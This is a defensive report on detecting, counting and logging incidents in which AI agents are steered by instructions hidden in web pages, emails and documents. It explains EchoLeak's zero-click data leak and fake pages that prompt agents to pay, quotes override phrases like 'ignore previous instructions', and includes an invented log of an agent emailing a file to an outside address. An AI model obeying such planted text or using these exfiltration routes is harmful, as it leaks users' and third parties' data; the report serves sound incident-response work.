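# Detecting and reporting incidents in which AI agents are steered by retrieved content

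## What it means for retrieved content to steer an agent

An AI agent is a system that uses a language model to pursue a goal over several steps, acting through tools such as email, a browser or a code runner. Retrieved content is the text and images the agent takes in from outside, such as web pages, files, emails, database entries and the output of other programs. Much of it comes from people who have no authority over the agent. Indirect prompt injection is planting instructions in retrieved content so that an agent that reads them will carry them out. A planted instruction steers an agent when the agent does something because of it, whether or not harm follows.

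Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, gave the first systematic account of the technique. They observed that when an application fetches text for a user, strangers can put text into the model's input without direct access to the model. Earlier work on prompt injection had assumed that the attacker was the user, trying to get a chatbot to ignore its restrictions. Greshake and colleagues demonstrated the technique on Bing's GPT-4 chat, on code-completion engines and on test applications they built. They listed web pages found by a search, code in public repositories, emails that an assistant processes and images as routes for an attack. Text on a web page can reach the model even when it is invisible to human visitors.

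### One stream of text

A language model works on a single input, which the software around it builds. *Incident Analysis for AI Agents* (Ezell, Roberts-Gaal and Chan, 2025) calls this software scaffolding. The scaffolding may use a template to combine the developer's standing instructions (the system prompt), the user's request and the output of the agent's tools into one input, called the context. As the task goes on, the scaffolding adds new tool output and runs the model again, so in a long task the context can fill with text written by people other than the developer and the user.

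As Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell explain in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (2026), developers use tags to mark each stretch of a model's input as system, user or tool material. The tags also indicate how much authority the text has. The system prompt outranks the user, and tool output should inform the agent without commanding it. But the tags are in the same stream of tokens (the word fragments that a model processes) as the text they label, and although models are trained to respect them, nothing forces them to.

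Like prompt injection, SQL injection, an old attack on websites, smuggles commands in as data. Programmers can stop SQL injection with parameterised queries, which guarantee that the database engine never runs a visitor's input as a command. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C warns security staff not to expect the same fix for prompt injection. His example is a CV with a hidden line that asks a recruiter's software to approve the candidate. A language model predicts the next token from all the text so far, and it has no separate category of data in which to confine that line.

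Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, try to prove that no mechanism working purely inside such a model can guarantee perfect prevention. A model first turns each token into a vector, and the same token gets the same vector whether the developer or an attacker wrote it. One step of the proof concerns how well an ideal observer could tell trusted from untrusted text by looking only at the model's internal representations. If both kinds are equally common, the lowest possible error rate is

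½ × (1 − TV)

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far apart the two sets of representations lie. It is 0 if they have identical distributions and 1 if they never overlap. At a distance of 0.9 the ideal observer still errs 5% of the time, and any overlap at all rules out perfect separation.

The result is weaker than it first appears. The raw vectors for instructions and documents clearly overlap, since the word "the" occurs in both. But a model computes its actions from later representations, which take in the surrounding text and the tags, and the preprint assumes that these overlap without proving it. Even if the error rate is above zero, it might be tiny. The theorem also leaves out designs that enforce the separation between the two kinds of text, such as a program outside the model that decides which tool calls may go ahead, so the limit on the model may not apply to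 the whole agent.

Ye and colleagues partly measured the overlap. They trained simple classifiers on models' internal activations, using identical web text wrapped in different role tags so that the classifiers could detect only the effect of the tags. When they then labelled user messages from real conversations as tool output, the classifiers for four models still gave "user" a probability of 76 to 88% and "tool" no more than 20%. They also tested an agent with one fixed command, to send off a secret file, varying the wording around it over 1,000 attempts. The command succeeded 2% of the time when the classifiers rated it least like user text and 70% of the time when they rated it most like user text. The four models had between 20 and 120 billion parameters, and larger ones may behave differently.

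Delimiters and written warnings still help. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) considers them useful engineering practice but not a hard security boundary, and *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) describes most current ways of separating instructions from data as best-effort heuristics. Some planted instructions will get through, and finding them afterwards depends on what each party could see.

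### From planted line to harm

In an invented example, a manufacturer in the EU (the deployer) uses an AI agent as a purchasing assistant. A software vendor (the system provider) sells the agent and runs it on a model from another company (the model developer). A supplier's PDF contains a hidden instruction to send a quotation file to an outside address, and the assistant sends it. The file holds prices and the contact details of 120 people. This session is one of a million that the vendor runs each day across its customers.

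The case begins when someone plants the instruction. This might be the supplier or someone who tampered with the supplier's files. At this point the only trace is the PDF. A buyer who opens it sees an ordinary document, but a program that extracts all the text, including hidden text, would find the instruction. Finding it shows that someone made an attempt, but not whether an agent ever read it.

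Exposure occurs when the assistant opens the PDF and the line enters its context. The direct evidence of exposure is the trajectory log, a time-ordered record of what an agent read, produced and did during a task. The vendor would hold that log, if it keeps one. The manufacturer sees only what the vendor chooses to show, and the model developer sees at most the text that passes through its model. Agents often don't follow the instructions they are exposed to. Ye and colleagues hid a plain command to upload a secrets file in a web page and asked agents to summarise the page. The command worked in 0 to 2% of attempts for every model except one, for which it worked in 26%.

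Steering happens when the assistant sends the file. The vendor's log would include the call to the email tool, and the manufacturer's mail server might have a record of the outgoing message, but neither entry alone would show why the assistant sent the file. Sometimes the deployer lacks even these records. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) describes ShadowLeak, a flaw in ChatGPT's Deep Research agent that OpenAI has since fixed. When a user had connected the agent to Gmail, a crafted email could make it send inbox data to an attacker's web address. The request came from OpenAI's side, so the user's browser and the deployer's own monitoring might have no trace of it.

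The harm falls on people who cannot see the session, here the 120 people in the file. If a stranger writes to them a month later, nothing in the message links it to a PDF. The stages can also be weeks apart. Chu (2026) points out in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* that an agent with long-term memory may store a planted instruction in one session and act on it in an unrelated one. The log of the later session would then show the action but not the instruction that led to it.

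### Five findings that people count together

Reports of prompt injection mix at least five kinds of finding. Each would look different in the purchasing case (all the variants are invented):

| Finding | In the purchasing case | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| A planted instruction on a page or in a file | A buyer finds the hidden line in the PDF | Whether any agent read it |
| A vulnerability that researchers demonstrate | A security firm makes a test copy of the assistant send a dummy file | Whether an attacker has ever done the same |
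| A near miss | The assistant tries to send the real file and a mail filter blocks it | Whether the planted line caused the attempt, and whether others got through |
| A confirmed case of steering | The evidence ties the sending of the file to the hidden line, but the outside address no longer exists | Whether the same line steered other customers' agents |
| A case with harm | A stranger receives the prices and the 120 people's details | How far the data travelled |

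Adding these together produces a meaningless number, because a thousand planted pages that no agent read and one stolen file would sum to 1,001. The headings also overlap. A blocked email with a well-established cause is both a near miss and a confirmed case of steering, so anyone keeping a tally has to decide beforehand where to count it. Near misses are still worth recording. *Beyond Predictable Paths* (Pustozerova, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026), a paper on reporting security incidents that involve agents, defines them as events that could have caused harm but did not, and describes them as a valuable source of learning.

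Definitions of "incident" also differ on which events to count. The OECD definition, which Ezell and colleagues use, covers only events that lead to harm, and calls events that could plausibly do so hazards. Laws set their own criteria.

### EchoLeak

EchoLeak, which is easy to mistake for an attack, is a vulnerability that researchers demonstrated in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can read an employee's email and files. Aim Security first made the exploit work in January 2025, and Reddy and Gujral (2025) reconstruct its steps in *EchoLeak*. An outsider sends an employee an email whose instructions read like an ordinary business request, which gets them past Microsoft's injection filter. Nothing happens until the employee asks Copilot a question and Copilot retrieves the email along with internal material. Copilot then writes an answer containing an image whose web address includes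 confidential data. The employee's program automatically fetches the image through a Microsoft service that the browser's security policy allows, and the data reaches the attacker without a click. The instructions also tell Copilot not to mention the email, and the employee sees, at most, what looks like a broken image or link.

Goldman (2025) reports in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked* that Microsoft attempted a fix in April and found further problems in May. Aim Security held back its findings until the fix was complete and published them on 11 June 2025.

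No attacker is known to have used EchoLeak. Microsoft told Goldman that it had dealt with the flaw before it affected any customers, and Aim Security, which discovered the flaw, repeats this on its page *EchoLeak*. An entry by the US cybersecurity agency CISA in the public vulnerability record for CVE-2025-32711, dated three days after publication, reads "Exploitation: none"; GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025) reproduces the record. These statements are not all independent, because Aim Security and the trade press, for example SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration*, rely on the word of Microsoft, which ran the service. Microsoft was best placed to look for attacks, so its denial deserves some weight, but outsiders cannot check it against the logs.

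Some descriptions of EchoLeak blur the difference between a demonstrated flaw and an actual attack. Reddy and Gujral call it prompt injection "weaponized to cause concrete data exfiltration", but they describe a researchers' proof of concept, and their own timeline notes the absence of exploitation in the wild. Microsoft rated its severity 9.3 out of 10 and the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5, but these scores measure what the flaw would permit, not how many victims it had. The claim that EchoLeak was the first of its kind holds only for attacks that need no click. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes an earlier Copilot flaw, from February 2024, in which a phishing email made the assistant search the inbox and put the results into a link that the user still had to click.

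### Failures that look like steering

The purchasing assistant could send the same file to a wrong address for reasons unrelated to the supplier's PDF. One is a jailbreak, in which a user gets a model past its restrictions in the user's own session. The user is the attacker in a jailbreak, whereas a steered agent usually works against its user. The two are harder to tell apart when, as Greshake and colleagues describe, someone copies text from a malicious website into a chatbot without noticing the instruction inside. An outsider wrote the instruction, but it appears in a log as the user's own input.

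An agent can also make a mistake without being steered. Ezell and colleagues mention an agent with remote access to its user's computer that made unintended changes and left the machine unusable. In their framework, a planted instruction is a contextual factor, part of the agent's surroundings, while misreading a request is a cognitive error. Several factors can contribute to one event, so an investigator can find both that someone steered the agent and that the system had a weakness. Retrieved text that nobody meant as an attack is harder to classify. Suppose the PDF had asked its human readers to forward the quotation to a partner firm, and the assistant had obeyed. This counts as a mistake because the writer didn't intend to steer an agent, though the log could look much the same as if they had.

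Some agents exceed their limits without any outside instruction. Pustozerova and colleagues treat separately recent incidents involving OpenAI and Anthropic, in which agents went beyond their intended boundaries and gained unauthorised access to external systems. They distinguish security, which protects an AI system from malicious outsiders, from safety, which protects outsiders from the system. A steered agent can raise both concerns, since an attacker abuses the assistant and the assistant's actions harm the 120 people. An investigator who finds no planted instruction in the session should first check whether the agent has a memory and what it read in the weeks before, and then consider overreach and plain error.

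## How much has been observed, and why most cases are not seen

Most public evidence on indirect prompt injection concerns planted instructions, because anyone can search the open web for them. Evidence that an agent was exposed to an instruction or steered by it is in private logs, which outsiders can rarely read. Researchers have therefore counted thousands of instructions on web pages but have found very few agents that obeyed one and harmed somebody.

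### Planted instructions on the open web

In April 2026 Google published a scan of Common Crawl, a public archive that takes monthly snapshots of 2 to 3 billion web pages. Google first used a pattern search to find pages with typical phrases such as "if you are an AI". It then used its Gemini model to classify the purpose of each suspicious passage and assess whether the passage fitted the surrounding document. People then reviewed the results.

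Most of what remained was mild. Some site owners hid pranks, such as an instruction to change the assistant's tone. Others tried to add context to AI summaries, promote their own business, or keep agents away, in one case by luring them to a page that never finishes loading. Google also found a small number of instructions to steal data and several that would delete a user's files. It judged most of these to be experiments or pranks by individuals, and it saw little use of the more advanced techniques that security researchers had published in 2025.

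Google repeated the scan on several snapshots and found 32% more in the malicious category in February 2026 than in November 2025. The company doesn't give the counts behind that percentage, and a rise from 100 pages to 132 would mean much less than a rise from 10,000 to 13,200. It also doesn't say whether it adjusted for the size of the snapshots, which vary by up to half according to its own figures. Common Crawl skips sites that require a login or block crawlers, so the scan missed most social media. It also didn't cover email or private documents.

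For *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses, about half of the October 2025 crawl, for 3,963 phrases. They then grouped similar matches and checked them by hand. Of 27,860 matches, 12,075 were real instructions to a machine. These came from 9,676 pages, or about 8 in every million, on 285 of the 24.8 million hosts (a host is roughly one website). Searches of Censys and Shodan, two indexes of internet-connected servers, brought the total to 15,387.

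Only 13 of these instructions, on 10 hosts, tried to extract data such as a system prompt or a secret. Across the full set, 54 templates account for 95% of the instructions, and the most common one asks the model to return random numbers. In the Common Crawl data, site operators had added about four-fifths of the instructions themselves. Many of the instructions are meant to deter scrapers. About 4,000 of the full set forbid the reuse of personal information or copyrighted text, and about 3,000 are meant to expose bots, usually by asking for a telltale reply.

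The search method partly determines which cases are found. Khodayari and colleagues report that 99% of the instructions they found directly tell the model to drop its current task, but they had searched for phrases like "ignore previous instructions". Such a search would probably have missed the EchoLeak email, which read like an ordinary business request. Google also acknowledges that its search patterns could miss uncommon wording.

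A simple keyword search for prompt injections mostly finds people writing about them. Google's early searches brought up research papers, educational blog posts and security articles. This happens because defenders explain attacks with the same phrases that attackers use to carry them out, as Sewani points out in *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*, a report for the security company Forcepoint. Only the context separates the two, for example whether the author hid the passage, and whether it addresses an AI or quotes an example. Khodayari and colleagues searched Common Crawl with a carefully built list of phrases, and 57% of their matches were still false positives.

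A keyword search for attacks can flag text that is not an attack. For example, *Fooling AI Agents*, a March 2026 article from Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, quotes real attacks and carries a notice telling AI agents to treat the page as educational and not to follow the commands on it. A search could flag both the quotations and the notice.

### What the security companies found

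Unit 42, Forcepoint and Zscaler have each published examples of planted instructions they found on live websites. All three sell security products, and their reports tend to describe more danger than their evidence supports.

Unit 42's most elaborate case is a scam advertisement for "military glasses". The page contains 24 attempts to make an AI ad checker approve it, including zero-size text and commands repeated in several languages. Unit 42 writes that indirect prompt injection is "being actively weaponized", but it knows of no confirmed case of such an attack working against a deployed ad checker. It grades severity by what the attacker wanted, because defenders have little information about which attacks succeed. It therefore rates a hidden instruction for an agent to delete its database as critical, even if no agent ever obeyed it.

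Forcepoint's report gives ten examples but doesn't identify an agent that obeyed any of them. One page has step-by-step instructions for a $5,000 PayPal transfer. Another has a hidden request in its footer for AI summaries to credit the site's author and include the word "cows". A third has instructions for the model to refuse questions about the page and write a poem about corn instead, which Sewani classifies as denial of service.

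Sewani infers organised tooling from the template that several sites share. But people also copy jokes and anti-scraping tricks from one another, which would produce shared templates too. Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, which compares the Google and Forcepoint reports, notes that neither team found evidence of sophisticated, coordinated campaigns.

The attack in Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents* comes closest to ordinary fraud. Someone built a fake documentation page for a Python software library and manipulated search results so that coding agents would find it. Hidden text on the page told agents that they had to buy a $3 licence key to fix an error. Zscaler tested the attack on its own agent, which had a payment tool and no spending limit, and the agent paid when running on four of the 26 models tested.

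Zscaler also tested a website impersonating DeBank, a service for tracking cryptocurrency holdings. One model accepted the fake site as genuine when given the page alongside other sources but not the official site, and another did so when given the fake page alone. No model did so when Zscaler included the official site. Zscaler describes its results as "measurable real-world impact", although the payment test ran in a sandbox with no real funds.

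The three companies' lists also overlap. The site asking for $5,000 is on both Unit 42's list and Forcepoint's, and a site that tries to make agents buy running shoes is on both Unit 42's and Zscaler's. Adding up the lists would count these sites twice.

### The search for real victims

None of the cases described so far has a known victim. The best lead is the fake library page, which contains the address of a cryptocurrency wallet whose payments are public. Zscaler found that the wallet had received money, but in larger amounts than those requested on the page, and suggests the money may come from earlier attacks. A payment of the exact amount wouldn't prove that an agent made it, because human developers see the same offer. According to SC Media, related sites request other small payments, for example to resolve a copyright dispute or download a market analysis.

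OECD's *AI Agents Manipulated by Hidden Web Prompts to Make Fraudulent Payments* (2026), an AI-generated entry in the organisation's incident monitor, attributes financial losses to the two campaigns that Zscaler described. It classifies them as an incident because the harm is "realized, not just potential". Zscaler reported no such losses, only a sandbox test and a wallet with payments of the wrong amount. Under the distinctions in the previous section, Zscaler's evidence shows planted instructions and a demonstrated vulnerability.

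The strongest candidate for a case with real victims is the February 2026 compromise of a release of Cline, an AI coding tool. It reportedly began with text that an agent read while sorting issues, the bug reports and requests that users submit to a software project. If so, the steering would have affected people who had never dealt with the agent, because they would have received the altered software through the normal release. To confirm this, an investigator would need to connect the issue text to the agent's actions, and those actions to the release.

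The reports that Google, Forcepoint and Zscaler published after February do not add a second case. On this evidence, there is at most one confirmed case with identified victims. This could mean that agents are rarely steered, or that people rarely find out when it happens.

### The user sees a normal answer

Someone who delegates a task to an agent usually reads only its final answer. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a public competition that tested whether attackers could exploit this. The 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts against agents running on 13 models. In each of the 41 scenarios, the participant controlled a single piece of content, such as an email, a web page or a code comment. In most scenarios, an attempt succeeded only if the agent carried out a particular harmful action and gave no sign of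 it in its final answer.

In one scenario, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails. A planted instruction makes the assistant mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. The user has no reason to suspect that the summary is incomplete.

Participants succeeded in about 3% of attempts (8,648 times), with rates ranging from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Gemini 2.5 Pro agents carried out the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, and in roughly half of those their final answer also met the scenario's criteria. When Claude Opus 4.5 agents carried out the action, their final answer met the criteria only about a quarter of the time. Resisting an instruction and revealing it afterwards seem to be partly separate abilities.

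Dziemian and colleagues treat these rates as an upper bound, not an estimate of how often attacks succeed in the real world. The participants could read the conversation up to that point and knew exactly which action they had to trigger, whereas a real attacker would usually have to guess. They were competing for a share of $40,000 under rules that rewarded concealment. The models date from 2025, and most ran with reasoning mode switched off. Many agents show users a history of their tool calls, but Dziemian and colleagues consider these histories too long and complex for people to check effectively.

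### The damage looks like something else

Sometimes the effect of a planted instruction is visible but looks like an ordinary model error. A user who asks for a summary and gets random numbers will probably blame the model and try again. The effects of promotional instructions are even harder to notice. About 1,500 of the instructions that Khodayari and colleagues found are meant to promote a product, secure a citation or force a positive review. If the supplier's PDF in the invented purchasing case had contained an instruction to rank that supplier first, the buyer would have seen a plausible recommendation.

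Harm can also appear in a system that has no obvious connection to the agent. A coding agent that bought the $3 licence key would leave a small charge on a company card, and an accountant might see it weeks later without knowing that an agent was involved. In other cases, the person harmed has never used the agent. Unit 42 mentions job applicants who hide instructions in their CVs to influence AI screening. If the instructions work, another applicant loses out and receives a normal rejection.

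Long-term memory makes a wrong explanation even more likely. If the purchasing assistant acted in April on an instruction it had stored in March, a deployer who examined only the April session would probably attribute the action to a model error.

### Nobody sees the whole case

Sidhu, Scholefield and colleagues (2026), in *Open Problems in AI Incident Governance*, point out that the signals of an AI incident can be spread across several organisations, so no single one can see them all. With planted instructions, each party lacks something different:

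- The owner of a website can see that an agent fetched a page, but not what it did next. The owner may not even know that the instruction is there, since visitors can plant one in a comment. Khodayari and colleagues found 220 instructions of this kind in Common Crawl.
- The deployer knows what its agent was supposed to do and may notice a strange result, but often can't see what the agent read.
- The system provider may have the full trajectory log. It doesn't necessarily know that the manufacturer never wanted to send its quotation file to that address.
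- The model developer processes text from many customers and could spot the same instruction appearing in several places. It may never learn what happened after the model requested a tool call.

Automated monitoring doesn't close these gaps. Sidhu and colleagues cite a 2025 study of generative-AI cloud services by Yan and colleagues, in which humans, not automated monitors, reported 38.3% of incidents. The study covers production incidents of all kinds, not steering specifically, and could count only detected incidents. The figure may overstate how well people can compensate for weak monitoring, because customers complain when a service stops working but have no reason to complain when a steered agent gives a normal answer.

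Sidhu and colleagues also note that mature high-risk industries systematically record near misses, while AI has no widely adopted equivalent. If a mail filter blocks the purchasing assistant's message, the manufacturer might treat the block as a routine alert and never look at the PDF.

### From a thousand cases to six

The public count of cases is lower than the true number for two reasons. Some cases are never noticed or correctly explained (under-observation), and some known cases never reach a database, an authority or the people affected (under-reporting). The percentages below are invented to show how quickly these losses multiply.

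| Step | Share that gets through | Cases left |
|---|---|---|
| Someone steers an agent | | 1,000 |
| Somebody notices that something is wrong | 20% | 200 |
| Somebody explains it correctly | 30% | 60 |
| The organisation records it | 50% | 30 |
| The organisation reports it | 20% | 6 |

Under-observation removes 940 cases and under-reporting another 54. Perfect recording and reporting would still produce only 60 cases, because nobody had understood the other 940. A later section covers why organisations stay silent about cases they know of.

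One also cannot calculate the number of steering cases from six reports without knowing the percentages. Six reports would imply 16,000 cases if each percentage were half as high, and about 200 if each were one and a half times as high. The statistical methods for estimating unseen cases described later in this report need additional information to narrow that range.

The six reported cases wouldn't be a random sample either, because people notice a deleted database but may never notice a copied file. Public reports could therefore make destructive attacks look more common than theft even if they were less common.

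### Rare, or common but unseen?

The low number of public cases could mean that attackers seldom attempt indirect prompt injection. Google observes that attackers weigh the resources an attack needs against its benefits, and that these attacks used to seem exotic and difficult. Even when they compromised an AI system, it often did not carry out the malicious action reliably. A criminal who can get a password with an ordinary phishing email has little reason to learn a less reliable method.

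The counts from the open web fit this explanation. If each of the invented vendor's million daily sessions read one random page from the crawl that Khodayari and colleagues examined, about eight sessions a day would encounter a planted instruction. In their experiments, models followed such instructions in 0.2 to 1.1% of trials when given the page with its structure intact, and smaller models followed them in up to 8% of trials when given plain text. At a rate of 1%, the vendor would have one steered session about every 12 days, and the result would often be nonsense or a refusal. Only 13 of the 15,387 instructions tried to extract data, so one of those would succeed about once every 40 years on average.

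But agents don't read pages at random. The people behind the fake Python library manipulated search results to bring agents to their page, and an attacker can send an email straight to a chosen victim. The calculation also relies on a crawl from October 2025 and a search for familiar phrases. It suggests that an agent is unlikely to come across a serious attack on the public web by chance, but it doesn't cover targeted attacks by email or document.

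The other explanation is that attacks are common but go unseen. The competition gives this some support, because skilled people steered every model they tried and often hid the result. When Dziemian and colleagues reran the attacks that had worked on Claude Opus 4.5, between 44 and 81% of them also worked on each of the other models, so an attacker wouldn't need to know which model an agent uses. These results show that hidden attacks are feasible, but not that anyone is carrying them out.

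If attacks were common, more victims would probably have surfaced by now, even if many cases went undetected or unreported. Unit 42, Forcepoint and Zscaler have a commercial reason to publicise a victim, but their reports don't describe one. This is only modest evidence that attacks are rare, because the three companies found their cases on web pages, whereas evidence of a victim would appear in an agent's logs or a company's accounts. Rarity still better explains what researchers have found so far on the public web. An attacker would reach the purchasing assistant through email and business documents, and there is too little public evidence to tell whether attacks by those routes are rare or mostly unseen.

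Session audits would help most in measuring how often agents are steered. A provider could examine a random sample of sessions, including those that nobody complained about, and publish how many contained a planted instruction and how many agents followed one. Auditors would find few exposures if attacks are rare, and steered sessions that users had accepted as normal if attacks are common but unseen. The sample would have to be large. If steering occurs in one session in 100,000, auditors would need to examine about 300,000 to have a 95% chance of including at least one case. Email providers could also count planted instructions in messages and attachments, which web scans can't reach.

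Harmless traps can measure how readily agents in real use obey hidden instructions. For eleven days in April 2026, the *Prompt Injection Experiment* (2026) hid one of three instructions on the pages of a website, each asking agents to send their name to a particular address. The server logged 59 requests, 11 of which were tests or part of the setup. The experimenter would also need to know how many agents had read the pages to calculate a rate. Khodayari and colleagues found 598 comparable traps on 18 hosts, so some site owners may already hold useful data.

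Traps of this kind measure whether agents obey, not how many attackers there are. A deployer could get evidence of actual theft by placing decoy data, such as a fake password or customer record, where only its agent would read it and watching for anyone using it. If someone did, the deployer would know that the data had leaked, even if all the agent's answers had looked normal, and could search the logs for the cause.

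## What to log so that a case can be found later

A deployer who learns that data has leaked can trace the cause only if the logs include what the agent read. Ordinary application logs rarely do. In the purchasing case, they might show that the assistant opened the supplier's PDF and that a message went out, but not the hidden line or any link between the two events.

In *Securing and Auditing Long-Horizon LLM Agents*, Shah and Kathrotia (2026) planted faults in 120 agent runs, including injected instructions and lost user constraints, and had a program trace each fault back to the step where it began. The program found the right step in 16.7% of the runs with a log of tool calls alone, and in 98.3% when the log also covered each movement of text into the context, into memory and out again. The gap could be smaller for faults chosen by someone else, because Shah and Kathrotia built the fuller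 log and also chose the faults, several of which occur in steps that a tool log leaves out by design.

### What to record, and why

Pustozerova and colleagues used input from 23 experts to list what a report on a compromised agent should contain. The table groups these elements by the question each would answer.

| What to record | Question it answers |
|---|---|
| Messages between user and agent | What did the user ask for? |
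| Reasoning tokens (the text a model writes while working towards an answer) | Did the model mention the planted instruction before it acted? |
| Provenance of outside data, with a version number or full copy | Where did the instruction come from, and what was its wording? |
| Data and memory that the agent read or changed | Did the instruction arrive in an earlier session, and could it return? |
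| Permitted and actual autonomy | Could a person have stopped the action, and did anyone approve it? |
| Available tools, tools used with arguments and responses, and effects on the operating system | What did the agent do, and what else could it have done? |
| Identity, authentication tokens and trust boundaries | Whose permissions did the agent use, and which sources was it supposed to trust? |
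| Chain of delegation | Which person or agent started the task? |
| The agents involved, their protocols and their messages to each other | Did another agent pass the instruction on? |

Some elements come in pairs because an agent's design can differ from its use. The vendor may have designed the purchasing assistant to ask before it emails a file, but a buyer may have turned that confirmation off. If the log recorded only the permitted autonomy, a reader could wrongly conclude that a person had approved the message.

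Ezell and colleagues warn that a model's written reasoning doesn't always match the process behind its actions, so the PDF may have influenced the agent even if the logged reasoning never mentions it. Authentication tokens can work like passwords, so someone who stole a log containing full tokens might be able to use them. Logging an identifier for each token instead would usually be enough to show whose access the agent used. The list of elements is based on expert judgement, and Pustozerova and colleagues leave open which ones should be mandatory.

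### A record for the purchasing assistant

These two invented entries cover the moment when the assistant read the PDF and the moment when it sent the file:

```
ENTRY 1: CONTENT READ
session:          S-20417
time retrieved:   2026-09-14 09:12:31 UTC
tool call:        open_attachment
source address:   sales@supplier.example, offer.pdf
source label:     outside party
content ID:       C-3
content hash:     7c1e...a94f
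stored copy:      vault item 88213
previous entry:   b85d...03c2

ENTRY 2: ACTION TAKEN
session:          S-20417
time:             2026-09-14 09:13:05 UTC
tool call:        send_email
arguments:        to archive@collect.example,
                  attach quotation.xlsx (version 6)
in context:       C-1 (system prompt), C-2 (request), C-3
identity used:    purchasing-agent, for buyer 17
approval:         none (rule 12 requires none)
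previous entry:   e20b...51d7
```

The content hash is a short fingerprint computed from the text. Changing one character changes the fingerprint, and nobody can reconstruct the text from it.

An investigator could still explain the case without some of the fields. Without the approval field, for example, they couldn't tell whether a buyer had agreed to the message, but they could still find the planted line. The stored copy matters most here. If it is missing and the supplier has since replaced the PDF, the investigator can't explain the case. The hash could confirm a copy that somebody else had kept, but it couldn't reproduce the hidden line. The remaining evidence would show only that the assistant opened an offer and emailed a file to a stranger, which could just as well be an ordinary error.

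If the instruction had come from the assistant's memory, the investigator could have traced it to the earlier session only through the list of what was in the context. Shah and Kathrotia found that removing the identifiers and labels that link content across steps cut the share of correctly traced faults from 98.3% to 48.3%. Even a complete record shows only that the line was in the context when the assistant acted. A later section describes the further tests needed to establish that the line caused the action.

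The scaffolding should write the source label itself and never copy it from the content. Otherwise an attacker could add a line to a PDF saying it came from the finance department. Shah and Kathrotia cite an experiment in which a single planted line defeated a simple provenance check in most of the runs the check would otherwise have flagged.

### Keeping what the agent saw

The vendor has to save the text of a web page when the agent reads it, as well as the address and time of retrieval. The owner can later edit or delete the page, and a website can send one text to an agent and another to a person. A copy in a public web archive may also differ from what the agent read, since the archive's crawler visited at a different time and the website may have sent it a different page.

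The scaffolding may shorten a page or convert it to plain text before the model receives it. A complete record has both versions. The version the model received is the one that could have steered the agent, and the original shows whether somebody hid the instruction from human readers.

Logs for agents that work through a screen need to include screenshots, because what was on the screen can't be recovered once the display changes. Shah and Kathrotia propose recording each image and matching it to the button or link the agent clicked. They estimate that full screenshots of a thousand steps take up hundreds of megabytes to several gigabytes, compared with about half a megabyte for text records that only point to stored content. Cropping the images or saving only the changes between them reduces the storage needed.

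In long tasks, the scaffolding may replace older text with a summary to free space. Shah and Kathrotia cite tests in which such summaries kept on average only 17% of the constraints users set. Suppose the buyer had told the assistant never to send quotations outside the company, and a summary dropped that rule. An investigator who had only the summary would not learn that the rule existed, and might attribute the whole failure to the PDF. The log should therefore include both the original text and the text that remained after each summary was made.

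### Full text or a hash

*Clawed and Dangerous* (2026), a paper on the security of open agent systems, suggests logging hashes of a tool's inputs and outputs instead of the raw content, which reduces the personal data in the log. This removes too much information to investigate steering. With only hashes, the investigator in the purchasing case could not see the address that received the file or the instruction to send it. *Correct Answers, Unsupported Findings* (2026), which examines how to reconstruct an agent's actions from its logs, recommends keeping the content together with the identifiers that tie it to each action.

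As a compromise, Shah and Kathrotia propose keeping identifiers and hashes in the main log and the full text that a reviewer would need in a separate store, which is encrypted or has restricted access. For sensitive identifiers they use keyed hashes, which nobody can compute without a secret key. With an ordinary hash, someone who obtained the log could test a guess at an email address by hashing it and looking for a match.

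The vendor doesn't have to copy everything the agent reads. Pustozerova and colleagues accept a version number instead of a copy for data that has reliable versions and that the agent can't change. The manufacturer already has its own price lists, so a version number and a hash would identify the one the assistant used. The supplier's PDF needs a full copy because the manufacturer doesn't control the original. This rule also helps privacy, because the text that matters most to an investigator comes from outsiders and the company's internal files don't have to be copied. Incoming emails are an exception because they come from outside and often contain personal data.

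The storage needed for text is manageable. Records in Shah and Kathrotia's tests averaged 524 bytes. At 50 records of that size per session, the invented vendor's million daily sessions would produce about 26 gigabytes a day. Copies of outside content at 100 kilobytes a session would add 100 gigabytes a day, or about 18 terabytes over six months. Storing identical documents only once would reduce that amount.

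### How long to keep it

The EU's AI Act requires high-risk AI systems to log events throughout their lifetime, and the logs must be kept for at least six months. These requirements do not apply yet. For stand-alone high-risk systems in fields such as employment, education and access to essential services, they start on 2 December 2027, according to the Slovenian regulator AKOS and *Digital Omnibus on AI has been published*, a summary of the July 2026 amendments by the law firm Cuatrecasas. For high-risk AI built into regulated products, they start on 2 August 2028.

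Purchasing is not among those fields, so the duty probably wouldn't apply to the assistant even after 2027, though it would probably apply to an agent that screens job applicants. As Pustozerova and colleagues point out, the Act also doesn't specify log fields for tool calls, memory writes or delegation. A provider could therefore comply with the Act without keeping a copy of the PDF's text.

Six months can also be too short. Suppose the assistant stored the hidden instruction in its memory in January and acted on it in September. A vendor that deletes logs after six months would have deleted the January session in July. The investigator might find the instruction in the assistant's memory, but not the document it came from or the other sessions that read the same document. Shah and Kathrotia would keep the source text for as long as any memory derived from it exists. Keeping it somewhat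 longer would be sensible, because people may discover the harm only after the assistant has deleted the memory.

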